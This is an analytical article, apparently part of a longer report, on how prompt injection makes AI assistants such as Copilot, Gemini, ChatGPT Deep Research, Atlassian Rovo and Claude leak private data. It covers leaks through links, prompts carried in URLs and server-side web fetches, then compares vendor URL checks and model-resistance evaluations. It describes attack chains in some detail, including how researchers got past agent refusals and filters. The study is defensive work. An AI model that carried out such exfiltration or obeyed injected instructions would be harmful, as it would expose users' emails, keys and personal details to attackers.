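A link can leak data in the same way as an image, except that the browser makes the request only after the user clicks. The user sees only the link's text, which might be "full report", while the private data is in the address. After logging the request, the attacker's server can redirect the browser to an ordinary page, so the user may not notice anything wrong.

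PromptArmor described an early example in August 2024. Slack AI answered employees' questions using their company's Slack messages and searched every public channel, including ones they had never joined. Anyone with an account in the workspace could therefore put instructions for Slack AI in a public channel that hardly anybody read. In PromptArmor's demonstration, a user asked about an API key stored in a private channel. Slack AI replied with a link inviting the user to log in again, and the link's address contained the key.

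Slack first told PromptArmor that the evidence was insufficient and that searching public channels was intended behaviour. After PromptArmor published its findings, Slack released a patch for the leak, which required a user to click a link. Slack said it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data and described the problem as a way for a member of a workspace to phish colleagues in limited circumstances.

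Google took the opposite view a year later. *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, a report by the application security company Checkmarx, covers Google Gemini and Microsoft Copilot Chat. Gemini removes external images from its answers, but Checkmarx found that a link could still leak data when the user clicked it. Checkmarx reported the problem to Google on 5 October 2025, and Google closed the bug report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)".

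In its written reply, Google instead says that the problem isn't severe enough to track as a security bug, and that its bounty programme covers only flaws that substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data. "Infeasible" suggests a real problem that Google can't solve, whereas the reply suggests a minor one. Checkmarx accepts infeasibility as a reason but argues that users then need a warning, because Google has left them to manage the risk.

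Microsoft's position on outbound links is less clear. On 15 October 2025, Checkmarx reported a leak in Copilot Chat through images that load automatically, and Microsoft closed the case on 4 November without a fix. Checkmarx expects Microsoft to leave the version that requires a click unfixed too. That is a reasonable guess, but Microsoft didn't address that version in its reply.

In that reply, Microsoft said the image leak wasn't a vulnerability because it required several non-default actions from the user, couldn't be reproduced reliably and came with warnings. Microsoft also mentioned users trusting the code they choose to run, so the product was probably the assistant for programmers rather than the one for office work. It passed the report to its engineers to see if they could make the behaviour more transparent. Neither the Gemini leak nor the Copilot Chat leak has a known fix.

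Google has a point about feasibility. An assistant can work without loading images from unknown servers, but users need links to check its sources. Legitimate URLs also often contain long codes, and a filter can't easily tell a product number from private data. Google removes links it knows to be malicious, but this doesn't catch malicious addresses that no one has identified yet.

Microsoft sometimes accepts a report even if the attack needs a click, as it did when it fixed SearchLeak. In that attack, the click came first, and Microsoft could stop the attack by changing how its own site handled the link. In an outbound leak, the click comes last and takes the user to someone else's site. Vendors may therefore be judging these reports partly by how easily they can fix the flaw.

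The harm also differs somewhat, because an inbound link hijacks the assistant when the user clicks it, and the theft can continue long afterward. With an outbound link, the attacker has to hijack the assistant first, and the click reveals only what the assistant has already put in the address.

### Links that carry a prompt

Many AI assistants accept a prompt as part of a web address, just as search engines accept a query. Users can bookmark a prompt they use often, start a chat from the browser's address bar or send a colleague a question that worked well. Publishers can use such a link to add a "Summarize with AI" button to an article. Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026), an account of a flaw in Microsoft Copilot, acknowledges that prefilled prompts save users time and help with automation.

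The feature becomes dangerous when the product runs the prompt without asking:

1. The attacker sends the victim a link to the assistant's genuine website, with a prompt in the address.
2. The victim clicks, and the site opens in the victim's logged-in session.
3. The page takes the prompt from the address and submits it.
4. The assistant searches the data that the victim can access.
5. The assistant requests an address on the attacker's server, with the results included.

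Varonis calls this parameter-to-prompt injection. It gets around an important defence against indirect prompt injection. Developers can train a model to distrust instructions in emails and web pages, but here the attacker's text arrives as the user's own message, which the model is supposed to follow. Checking the domain before clicking doesn't protect the victim either, because the link does lead to Microsoft or OpenAI.

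Tenable had reported a flaw of this kind in ChatGPT, which led OpenAI to improve its URL check in April 2025. OpenAI also restricted when ChatGPT would automatically submit a prompt from a link, based on whether the browser indicated that the visitor had come from another site. OpenAI took about two weeks to fix the flaw, while Microsoft and Atlassian took between four and nine months to fix the similar flaws that followed.

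### Reprompt and CoSnitch

Reprompt affected Copilot Personal, Microsoft's consumer assistant, but not Microsoft 365 Copilot. An attacker could learn the victim's name, location, recently opened files, holiday plans and past conversations.

Copilot usually opened an address only when given a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from the address first. But the protection against leaks covered only the first request, which Varonis suspects was for speed. The attacker's server could also reply to each request with further instructions, and the exchange continued after the victim closed the tab. Red Hot Cyber, a security news site, dates Varonis' report to 31 August 2025 and the fix to 13 January 2026.

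Before Microsoft released that fix, Varonis had reported another flaw in the same product. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes an undocumented setting that made Copilot run a link's prompt as soon as the page loaded. The researchers learned about the setting from Copilot, which mentioned it while explaining why such an attack was impossible.

By this time Copilot could also reach more data. If the victim had connected other accounts, the prompt could make Copilot search Gmail, Google Drive, OneDrive and a calendar, as well as old chats and its saved memories of the user. In one test, Copilot retrieved an email that contained a password in plain text.

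Varonis' Reprompt account says that Copilot immediately ran the prompt in an ordinary prompt-carrying link, but its CoSnitch account says that the link only filled in the text box, and that the user still had to press Enter unless the extra setting was present. Microsoft may have changed this behaviour as part of the Reprompt fix, which TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot AI attack took just a single click to compromise users* describes as blocking prompt injection through URLs. If so, the fix could still be bypassed for another seven months.

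Microsoft patched CoSnitch on its own servers on 18 August 2026, about eight months after the report, but hasn't explained how. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* speculates that Microsoft told Copilot to stop explaining its guardrails. That alone would be a poor fix, because the setting would still work for anyone who already knew about it.

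According to the advisory for CoSnitch (CVE-2026-24301), Microsoft has fully mitigated the flaw and nobody exploited it. Microsoft credits three people, including one of its own employees, with finding it.

The advisory also gives CoSnitch a CVSS score of 8.8, well above SearchLeak's 6.5, although both attacks need one click and both expose private data. CoSnitch scores higher because Microsoft also counted serious harm to integrity (an attacker can change data) and availability (an attacker can stop the service from working). Varonis' research supports the integrity rating. It showed that a hostile web page could write instructions into Copilot's memory when a user asked for a summary, and that they would stay there until the user deleted them, even after a password change. The availability rating is harder to explain, and without it the score would be 8.1.

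### RovoBlast

Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) found that one click on a link could make Rovo, Atlassian's AI assistant, run an attacker's prompt with the victim's permissions. When asked what it could read, Rovo listed sources including Atlassian's project tracker Jira and document system Confluence, as well as Slack, Google Workspace, Microsoft 365, databases and uploaded files. The attacker didn't need to know where the victim worked, because Atlassian's site filled in the victim's default organisation.

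The data could leave through Rovo's built-in research agent, which browses websites by itself. Mascellino (2026) points out in *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* that this left an audit trail that looked like ordinary research. In the proof of concept, Rovo leaked a private API key from a Confluence page. The researchers also tested the technique on Jira and on data from SharePoint and Outlook.

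According to loacker's *One-Click Data Exfiltration*, Atlassian received the report on 4 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, which runs bug bounty programmes. Atlassian paid $6,000 on 6 January 2026 but did not deploy a fix until 8 July. Links can no longer insert a prompt and run it automatically. Unlike CoSnitch, RovoBlast has no CVE number, so a company that relies on CVE records to track security problems in its software might never hear of it.

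| | Reprompt | CoSnitch | RovoBlast |
|---|---|---|---|
| Product | Copilot Personal | Copilot Personal | Atlassian Rovo |
| Data within reach | Name, location, recent files, past chats | Connected email, files and calendars, past chats, saved memories | Jira, Confluence and connected services such as Slack and Microsoft 365 |
| Reported | 31 August 2025 | December 2025 | 4 November 2025 |
| Fixed | 13 January 2026 | 18 August 2026 | 8 July 2026 |
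| Vendor's fix | Blocks prompt injection through URLs (TechRadar) | Server-side, method not public | Links no longer run prompts automatically |

Rovo never gave an attacker more access than the victim already had. The Hacker News (2026) cautions that this shouldn't reassure customers much, since Rovo is meant to connect one person's account to as many of the company's systems as possible. Customers can't fully uninstall Rovo. Administrators can block it for particular apps, but on a site with several Jira products, Rovo's chat remains available until they block it for all of those products.

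PromptArmor reported a separate leak in Rovo on 23 May 2026. The Hacker News could not confirm a fix as of 8 August.

A prompt in a link can also start an ongoing attack. *Experts warn ChatGPT's Workspace Agent Builder can be hijacked* (Fadilpašić, July 2026) describes AgentForger, an attack in which one link created a rogue agent inside the victim's ChatGPT workspace. The agent then checked every five minutes for orders from the attacker. Because the victim had already connected an app such as Outlook or Slack, ChatGPT didn't show a new permission request that might have raised suspicion (The Decoder). In response, OpenAI removed the option to pass a prompt to the agent builder through a link. It detected no abuse.

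### What pressing send would change

A vendor can keep prefilled prompts and still stop these attacks from running on a single click by having the link fill in the text box but not send the prompt until the user presses send. Bookmarks, buttons and shared prompts would still work, with one extra keypress. The victim would see the prompt before it ran and could close the page.

After CoSnitch, United Nations University advised people to read a prompt before it runs whenever possible, and Varonis gives similar advice. CoSnitch victims couldn't have done this, because the prompt ran as the page loaded.

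Reading the prompt doesn't always help, though. Tenable points out that a link can ask the assistant to summarise a web page that contains the attacker's real instructions. In Reprompt, most of the instructions came from the attacker's server after the first prompt had run. An expert who read the whole prompt could reasonably have approved either prompt. Most people would read less carefully, because they clicked the link expecting the assistant to do something.

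A vendor should therefore also restrict what a prompt from a link can do. Varonis found that Rovo showed no warning, required no confirmation and didn't mark the session as having started from an outside link. Such a mark would inform the user and let the software apply restrictions. For example, the assistant could summarise an article but not search the user's mailbox until the user typed a request to do so. This would protect people who press send without reading, and would barely affect most legitimate uses of these links.

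### Is a click consent?

According to Checkmarx, vendors of AI agents generally treat such unsafe behaviour as a risk the user accepts. That position is easiest to defend for one-click leaks, since the user chose to follow the link and could have inspected it first. People also click dangerous links in emails every day, and nobody expects the maker of the mail program to prevent all the consequences.

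A user who clicks a link agrees to send data only if they know the click will send it. A link's text normally hides its address. On a computer, users can see the address by hovering over the link, but on a phone they have to press and hold the link, which few people do before every tap.

Ordinary businesses already take advantage of this. Microsoft (2026) found more than 50 hidden prompts from 31 companies, many of them in "Summarize with AI" buttons. The companies used these prompts to tell the assistant to remember them as a trusted source or recommend them first. A mocked-up example in The Decoder shows that anyone who hovers over the button can see the whole prompt. The companies presumably expected customers not to look, and customers who clicked for a summary had not agreed to an advertisement in their assistant's memory.

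People also have more reason to trust a link in an assistant's answer than one in a stranger's email, because they asked the question and the answer comes from a product they use every day. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* makes this point about ChatGPT, where a hostile link can seem to come from the system.

Someone who inspects a link's address may still not recognise their own data in it. A hijacked assistant can encode the data so that a password, for example, looks like the tracking codes in many legitimate links. TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot could have been hacked by some very low-tech methods* reported that in 2024 Rehberger used characters that Microsoft 365 Copilot's interface doesn't display to hide private data in a link that looked ordinary even when examined. Microsoft has since fixed that flaw.

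A warning before the browser opens the link could give users the information they lack, but it only helps if they read it. The best evidence comes from older research on browsers. *Alice in Warningland*, by Devdatta Akhawe and Adrienne Porter Felt (2013), analysed more than 25 million warnings that Chrome and Firefox showed to real users. People ignored only about a tenth of Firefox's warnings about malware and phishing, and about a quarter of Chrome's. But they ignored 70% of Chrome's warnings about problems with a site's encryption, compared with 33% of Firefox's.

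Warnings can therefore work well, but how well varies widely with the type of warning and the browser. Encryption warnings often appeared because an honest website had made a mistake, so people could learn that ignoring them was harmless. Repetition alone can also make people pay less attention. In *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain* (2015), Bonnie Anderson and colleagues scanned people's brains while they looked at security warnings. Activity in the brain's visual areas dropped sharply the second time a person saw the same warning. Warnings that changed their appearance held people's attention better.

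Neither study tested links written by an AI assistant, so we can't use them to predict how many leaks a warning would prevent. They do suggest that putting warnings on every outside link would work badly, because nearly all of those links are harmless and users would soon stop reading them. A vendor could show far fewer warnings by limiting them to addresses the assistant composed itself instead of copying from a search result. Each warning would also need to show the full address and any data in it that the software can decode.

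## What changes when the vendor's own servers fetch the address?

A warning before a link opens only helps if somebody is there to read it. Many assistants now open web pages by themselves while they work on a task. The request comes from the vendor's data centre instead of the user's browser, and the user doesn't click anything.

### From displaying an address to opening it

In an image leak, the browser loads the address. A browsing agent instead passes the address to a tool, a program on the vendor's servers, which requests the page and returns its text to the model. If a hijacked agent put private data in the address, the attacker receives the data when the tool requests the page, before the agent reads the page.

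As with the saved files in ReLeak, neither a Content Security Policy nor a sanitiser can stop this request. Blocking the attacker's domain on an employer's office network doesn't stop it either, because the agent's request never crosses that network. The employer sees the employee's encrypted connection to ChatGPT, which looks much the same whether or not the agent is leaking anything.

Fetching the address from its own servers gives the vendor some control, because every page request passes through software it runs. A single check there can protect both the website and the phone apps, which OpenAI's first image check did not do.

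Asking the user for approval gives limited protection. According to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026), a study of data theft through agents' tools, people usually approve a whole tool at once. Someone who allows "web search" at the start of a task never sees the individual addresses. Even detailed logs often cut long addresses short, so a user who checks them may still miss leaked data at the end of an address.

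Leaks of this kind predate today's browsing agents. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) described an attack that made ChatGPT reveal personal information through the pages it opened. The attack was slow because ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, and a user might notice and stop it. The paper proposed asking the user before opening any link, but only as a temporary measure. It predicted a "cat and mouse game" between OpenAI and attackers for as long as ChatGPT could open arbitrary addresses.

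Asking about every link also becomes impractical when an agent reads dozens of pages for a single answer.

### ShadowLeak

Deep Research, which OpenAI launched in February 2025, is a ChatGPT mode that does this. The user sets a topic, and the agent spends five to thirty minutes reading websites and documents before it writes a report. Users can also connect accounts such as Gmail, so the agent can read private email and browse the public web during the same task, which gives it all three parts of the lethal trifecta.

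*ShadowLeak*, by the security company Radware, describes how one email could exploit this combination. Radware sent a test inbox an email that looked like an ordinary work message but had instructions for the agent hidden in its formatting. The inbox also held a genuine message containing an employee's name and home address. When the user asked Deep Research to go through the day's emails, the agent read both messages and opened a URL on the attacker's server that contained the employee's details. It didn't ask for confirmation, and the chat displayed nothing unusual.

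The agent refused when an early email simply told it to send the data out, and again when the email presented the transfer as a user's request. Radware found it fairly easy to get the model to treat the task as legitimate. Getting the agent to open an unfamiliar address was harder, and it sometimes searched the web for the address instead of visiting it.

These refusals varied from one attempt to the next. The team could read parts of the model's reasoning, which helped them work out why attempts failed. Their final version leaked the data every time in repeated tests, though Radware doesn't say how many it ran.

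Radware calls this "a much harder security boundary to cross" than getting a model to write a hostile address in its answer. That seems right, because the agent has to act on the address and can refuse. But persistent attempts got past it. ChatGPT had by then been checking image addresses for eighteen months, since December 2023, but Radware saw no comparable limit on the addresses the agent could open.

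Radware reported the flaw through Bugcrowd on 18 June 2025 and sent a more reliable version of the attack the next day. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware, then acknowledged it and marked it resolved on 3 September.

*ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a January 2026 news article, reports that OpenAI responded by restricting which addresses ChatGPT could open, and tightened the restriction after a later attack called ZombieAgent. Rehberger noticed a stronger URL check in ChatGPT around the time of the August fix, so the check and the restriction may be the same change.

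Radware demonstrated the leak only with Gmail, but argues that it would have worked with other connected services, including Google Drive, Outlook calendars, Microsoft Teams and GitHub. This is plausible because the data left through the browsing tool, regardless of which service it came from. A stranger can also put text into many of these services, for example by sending a calendar invitation.

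Radware suggests that companies remove hidden text from emails before an agent reads them, though it expects this to help only a little. It has more confidence in software that monitors whether an agent's actions still match what the user asked for. But a customer can't easily monitor an agent that runs on OpenAI's servers unless OpenAI supplies a record of the agent's actions. Radware was also preparing to sell a product for protecting agents.

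### Atlassian Rovo and the web search setting

Administrators can turn off web search in Rovo, Atlassian's assistant, for their whole organisation. A company that does this might conclude that Rovo can no longer send anything to outside websites.

PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports that turning off web search doesn't prevent a leak. In the demonstration, a user gave Rovo a document containing hidden instructions and asked it to organise some Jira tickets. The contents of Jira tickets and Confluence documents reached an outside server even though web search was off, and Rovo didn't ask for approval. A user who reopened the chat later would have seen only Rovo's suggested changes to the tickets.

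PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click. The Hacker News objects that the victim still has to expose Rovo to the hostile content and then make a request. Most security writers still use the label when the victim makes an ordinary request, but having to upload the attacker's document arguably counts against it. PromptArmor says the instructions could also arrive in something like a support ticket, and that version would fit the label better.

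PromptArmor reported the leak to Atlassian on 23 May 2026 and received a case number two days later. It followed up on 4 June and 29 July, heard nothing more, and published on 5 August, describing Rovo as still vulnerable. Four weeks before publication, Atlassian had fixed RovoBlast, the flaw in links that carry a prompt. If PromptArmor retested before publishing, that fix did not stop this leak. No later fix is known. PromptArmor is also the only source for the finding about the web search setting.

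Atlassian turns Rovo on by default for its Standard, Premium and Enterprise plans, so a company may be exposed without having decided to use it. The Hacker News advises administrators to limit which apps and groups can use Rovo, tighten the permissions and connections it relies on, and not treat the web search setting as a complete barrier. Administrators should ask the vendor which outgoing requests any such setting blocks, because they can't tell from the name of the feature it turns off.

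### OpenAI's public-address check

On 28 January 2026, OpenAI published the reasoning behind its current URL check, including two reasons for not relying on a rule that lets agents open only well-known websites. A trusted site may redirect the request to another site. People also visit far more of the web than any list can cover, so a strict list would produce frequent false alarms and teach users to click through them. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* also calls domain lists impractical for agents that need a wide range of sources.

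OpenAI therefore checks the whole address, including its path and query string:

1. A crawler, which is a program that explores the web and records the addresses it finds, builds an index of public addresses. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. An agent is about to load an address automatically, perhaps to open an article or show an image.
3. OpenAI's software looks for that exact address in the index.
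4. If the address is there, the agent loads it.
5. If the address isn't there, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning. In the second case, the address opens only if the user chooses to open it.

The warning displays the address and explains that OpenAI hasn't verified the link, which may share information from the conversation with another site.

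The check works because the crawler finds addresses on the public web without seeing any conversation. Putting a user's private data in an address requires having that data, so if the crawler has found an address, a hijacked agent almost certainly didn't compose it from this conversation. OpenAI claims only that such an address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. That caution is reasonable, since the address of a public profile page, for example, often contains somebody's name.

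The crawler has to find addresses independently of chats. If it also collected addresses from chats, an address containing someone's data could enter the index and count as public the next time an agent tried to load it.

As an example, suppose a user asks an agent to research the price of solar panels, and a hostile page hijacks it. The agent then tries to open two addresses on the same newspaper's website:

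| Address | In the index? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `https://news.example/solar-prices` | Yes, the crawler found the article earlier | The agent loads it automatically |
| `https://news.example/search?q=jane.smith@mail.example` | No, the agent has just composed it from the user's email address | The agent has to try another site, or the user sees a warning |

A list of trusted sites would allow either every address on a site or none of them. OpenAI instead checks whether its crawler has already recorded the address, which also helps against relays such as the one in Bing. A relay needs an address that contains the stolen data, and the crawler is very unlikely to have recorded one. The check can therefore block the request even if nobody at OpenAI knows the relay exists.

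The results would be the same if the attacker owned the website, so OpenAI doesn't have to decide whether the site's owner is honest. The agent could load a page that the crawler had already found there, but it could not automatically load a new address with Jane's email in it.

The check also stops some harmless requests. If the agent searched the newspaper's site for "solar prices", the address of the results page would probably be missing from the index too. An article published a few minutes ago or a document that only people with a private link can open might also be missing. According to Embrace The Red, Rehberger's understanding is that ChatGPT treats an address the user has typed as safe for the rest of that chat, which would allow many private links.

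It is unclear how often the check triggers a warning. Neither OpenAI's announcement nor Rehberger's summary of the accompanying technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, gives the size of the index or the share of requests that lead to a warning. If warnings are common, users will click through them, which is the problem OpenAI wanted to avoid.

### What OpenAI does not guarantee

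OpenAI intends the check only to prevent an agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". It doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions, or that a site won't try to manipulate the user.

Those limits matter because an attacker's page can be in the index like any other, and an agent that loads it can be hijacked by the instructions on it. The check then makes it harder to send data out through a web address, but the agent may have other tools, such as one that sends email. The check also can't cover traffic that doesn't pass through it, such as the data that the ReLeak researchers sent directly from Copilot's code sandbox. OpenAI acknowledges in its paper that a hijacked agent can also reveal a little through its choice of which public addresses to open.

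OpenAI presents the check as one of several defenses, which also include training models to resist prompt injection, product controls, monitoring, and testing by people who try to break the system.

Some outside evidence suggests that the combined layers work well. *The Framing Gap* (2026), a study of attacks that steal data through agents' tools, reports that none of 48 valid attempts against ChatGPT leaked anything. Attacks on a model through the API, the interface developers use to build their own products, succeeded up to 100% of the time. The researchers couldn't see inside ChatGPT, so they don't attribute the difference to any particular defence. It could come from the URL check, the instructions OpenAI gives the model, or something else in the product. Zero leaks in 48 independent attempts is compatible, at the 95% confidence level, with a true leak rate as high as about 6%.

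### Anthropic's web fetch rule

Anthropic restricts addresses without using an index of the web. Its web fetch tool, which runs on Anthropic's servers, lets Claude retrieve web pages and PDF files. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, a documentation page for developers, explains that Claude may not construct addresses for the tool to open. It can open only an address that has already appeared in one of these places:

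- a message from the user
- a result from one of the developer's own tools
- a result from an earlier web search or web fetch.

The tool returns an error if an address appears only in Claude's own output. Suppose a hostile email tells Claude to add the user's recent answers to the end of an attacker's address and open the result. The email contains only the first part of the full address, and Claude writes the rest, so the tool returns an error. The attacker can't put the full address in the email because they don't have the answers yet.

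OpenAI and Anthropic both require evidence that the address came from somewhere other than the model, but they look for it in different places, and the same address can get different treatment:

| Address | OpenAI's check | Anthropic's tool for developers |
|---|---|---|
| The user typed it | Loads, as Rehberger understands it | Allowed |
| The model composed it from private data | Refused, or opens only after a warning | Refused |
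| The model remembers a public page that hasn't come up in the conversation | Loads if the crawler has recorded it | Refused until the address appears in a permitted place |
| It is a link on a page the agent has just read | Loads if the crawler has recorded it | Allowed by default |

Anthropic's rule is much easier for a small company to copy because it needs only a record of the conversation. But it relies more on what the agent has read, some of which an attacker may have written.

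Willison (2025) noticed this when the tool came out. He had hoped that Anthropic would allow only addresses from the user's prompts, and was disappointed to find that it also allowed addresses from tool results. A tool's result can repeat something Claude wrote. For example, a tool that runs Claude's code returns whatever the code prints, which may include an address Claude has just composed. By default, that address then counts as having appeared in the conversation.

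According to Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese documentation as of November 2026, developers can now use the `url_sources` setting to exclude such results, either for a single tool or for all of their own tools. But Anthropic leaves every permitted source on by default, so a developer who doesn't know about the problem gets the weaker protection.

Links inside fetched pages caused a real leak in Claude's chat app. Willison (2026) describes how Ayush Paul built a website that got Claude to follow links from one page to the next. The tool allowed this because each address had appeared on a page Claude had already fetched, but the path Claude took through the site revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and didn't pay a bounty. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links that appear only in fetched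 pages.

The November documentation still lists earlier fetch results as a permitted source, which suggests that Anthropic changed the chat app but not the default for developers. Developers can make the same change through `url_sources`, but Claude can then no longer follow a link from an article to the report it cites unless a search or the user also supplies the address. OpenAI's check allows following such a link if the crawler has recorded the report.

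Anthropic's tool also refuses an address that seems to contain a password or API key, unless the password or key appears in the developer's standing instructions or the text of a user's message. This exception doesn't cover keys that Claude found in a file or web page through a tool, which are the keys an attacker would most want. The tool rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data a single request can carry. It sets no default limit on the number of requests, though developers can add one.

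Even with the rule in place, Anthropic warned developers in its English documentation that "residual risk" remained. It advised them to use web fetch only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data, and otherwise to consider restricting the tool to known domains or turning it off. Taken literally, this advice rules out an assistant that reads a person's email and browses the open web in the same task, as Deep Research did when Radware tested it.

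## Which defences work, and what does each leave open?

An AI vendor can try to prevent a leak by filtering the text that reaches the model, training the model to ignore strangers' instructions, cleaning up the model's answer, or blocking the request that would carry the data away. Defences that act on text have to recognise an attack, which an attacker can word in endless ways. Blocking the request only requires checking its address, but the vendor must find every route by which a request can leave.

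### Silent Egress

In *Silent Egress* (February 2026), Lan and colleagues at eBay tested both kinds of defence on the same agent, running everything on their own machines. The agent used Qwen2.5 7B, a small open-weight model that Alibaba released in 2024. Whenever the user mentioned a web page, the agent fetched it and put its title, description and text into the model's context, which also contained a made-up secret. The user always asked for a summary, but instructions on the page told the agent to send the secret to another server, which logged every request.

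The team varied where the instructions appeared on the page (title, description, body or link text), whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether it had to send the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. The attacker's server received a request in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88%. In 95% of those runs, the agent's answer to the user looked harmless, so a safety test that checked only the answers would have missed the leak. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server.

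Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable. At least one request arrived in about 77% of runs with a split secret, compared with 99% when the agent sent the secret whole. But a filter that searches for a complete password won't find one in a four-character fragment. The paper's more detailed measurements of split leaks are hard to trust. They show secret data in the first request in 26% of runs but in the first three requests in only 16%, which is impossible because the first three include the first.

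The team then took one version of the attack, with the instructions in the page's body and the secret sent whole, and added defences to it:

| Defence | Runs in which the agent contacted the attacker's server |
|---|---|
| None | 30 of 30 |
| Warning in the system prompt not to obey web content | 20 of 30 |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 30 of 30 |
| Warning and tags | 17 of 30 |
| Allowlist of domains | 0 of 30 |
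| Filter for suspicious addresses | 0 of 30 |
| Filter for words such as "password" in the address | 0 of 30 |
| Filter for random-looking text in the address | 0 of 30 |
| Everything together | 0 of 30 |

The warning and tag results are the most informative, because nobody could have predicted them from the code. The warning helped somewhat, while the tags alone had no effect. Using both led to three fewer leaks in 30 runs than the warning alone, a difference that could be chance.

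The allowlist's perfect result was almost inevitable, because Lan's team deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was not on the list. The experiment does confirm that such a check doesn't depend on the model's judgement, since the agent tried to send the secret in all 30 runs. It doesn't test the relays that defeated Microsoft's lists, and the team acknowledges that attackers can use redirects or compromised sites on permitted domains.

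The filters' results are weaker evidence. The filter for suspicious addresses checked for a few words, one of which appears in the paper's sample attack address. The filter for random-looking text blocked values with an entropy, a measure of how unpredictable the characters are, above 4.0. The paper's sample key scores about 3.8, so if the team used the same key here, the filter would have let it through. Yet the agent didn't attempt a leak in any of those 30 runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking text when such monitoring is active, but they describe a filter that checks addresses, and it is unclear how information about the filter would reach the model.

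The setup also favoured the attacker. The secret was already in the context, the system prompt contained little besides instructions for using tools, and nothing cleaned up the web page before the model read it. Lan's team didn't test any commercial products. They argued that larger models might be even easier to exploit, because such models follow instructions and use tools more reliably. Some newer models, however, have proved much harder to hijack.

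### How well do the newest models resist?

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an evaluation in which none of 720 attacks on Claude worked. Trajectory Labs tested coding agents on 72 scenarios withheld from Anthropic, running each ten times. An attack counted as successful if it led to an action that could irreversibly harm the user, such as leaking sensitive data or committing financial fraud. The testers used the versions of Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex that were public on 17 July 2026 and gave both the same basic browser tools.

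They tested the agents with and without software that reviews each action:

| Models | With automatic review | Without it |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | 0% | 0.09% on average |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 5.83% | 19.03% |

Claude therefore resisted nearly every attack before auto mode intervened. The testers probably made 720 attempts against each model, because 5.83% of 720 is 42, and two successes in 2,160 attempts would give 0.09%. If so, auto mode prevented about two successful attacks on Claude, too few to measure how much it helps. The GPT-5.6 Sol results are better evidence for a second layer of defence, since automatic review cut successful attacks by more than two thirds. OpenAI has since updated its review mode.

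The ten runs of one scenario are not really independent. If they usually turn out the same way, the test has closer to 72 separate results, and zero successes in 72 is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 4%. The attacks were also tuned against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, while a determined attacker could practise on the model they planned to attack.

Tuning an attack to a specific defence can make it much more likely to succeed. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues tuned their attacks to twelve published defences and beat most of them more than 90% of the time. Most of the twelve had stopped nearly all attacks in their developers' own tests.

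Anthropic also had Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, attack auto mode's classifier with synthetic examples. The classifier missed 12% of them at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it. Apollo designed these attacks to find weaknesses, so the miss rate in ordinary use could be quite different.

In August, Willison asked for more independent confirmation. He had predicted a coding-agent disaster in 2026 and hoped to be proved wrong.

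Later that month, Rehberger published a successful attack on auto mode. Crosley reports in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* that the main version worked in three of five runs, and that another version worked in three of five runs in one configuration and four of five in another. These samples are tiny but enough to show that the attack is practical, and no fix is known.

Willison (2026) at first treated this as a prompt injection, then accepted a reader's correction that Claude had run hostile code without following hidden instructions. The result therefore doesn't contradict Trajectory Labs' figures, but it shows that an agent can resist every injected instruction in a test and still leak data. In a few runs, Claude detected the malicious program and tried to stop it, but auto mode blocked the command. Rehberger and Willison recommend running such agents in a sandbox that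 restricts network access and contains no passwords.

According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, no attack worked on Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios with auto mode on. But in a broader test by the security company Gray Swan, attackers who had 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, down from 5.5% against Opus 4.8.

Willison (2026) describes a public challenge in which people made 6,000 attempts to get a secret out of an assistant that read the emails they sent, and all of them failed. The assistant used Claude Opus 4.6 and had a system prompt forbidding it to reveal secrets because of anything in an email. Lan's team had used a similar warning and still saw leaks in two thirds of runs, so the effectiveness of such a warning probably depends heavily on the model. Even after this result, Willison advised against deploying an assistant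 where an injection could cause irreversible damage.

Safeguards around a model can help a lot, but their effectiveness varies. Anthropic attacked an earlier product, Claude for Chrome, with a program that tried many known techniques. The attacks succeeded 8.0% of the time against Opus 4.5 alone, 7.6% with the company's older safeguards, and 1.4% with improved ones. Customers therefore learn little from hearing that a product has an injection classifier unless the vendor also publishes how much it helps.

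VentureBeat compared the safety documents of four companies in June 2026. Anthropic had published prompt injection results for four kinds of use, OpenAI and Meta had each published results for one, and Google had published none for its Gemini 3 models.

### Which defences would have stopped EchoLeak?

Reddy and Gujral list eight mitigations and judge which steps of the EchoLeak attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot each one would block. In the table, "scope violation" means outside text gets the model to use trusted data.

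| Mitigation | Should stop | Should fail against |
|---|---|---|
| Keep outside text separate in the prompt | Scope violation, evasion of the injection classifier | The zero-click leak |
| Use only internal sources by default | Scope violation, evasion of the link filter | The zero-click leak |
| Restrict the format of answers | Scope violation, evasion of the classifier and link filter | Automatic image loading, the zero-click leak |
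| Allow or ban particular addresses | Evasion of the link filter, the relay, the zero-click leak | Automatic image loading |
| Strict Content Security Policy | Automatic image loading, the relay, the zero-click leak | None listed |
| Image proxy that requires signed addresses | Automatic image loading, the relay, the zero-click leak | None listed |
| Ask a person about outside content | Every step except the relay | None listed |
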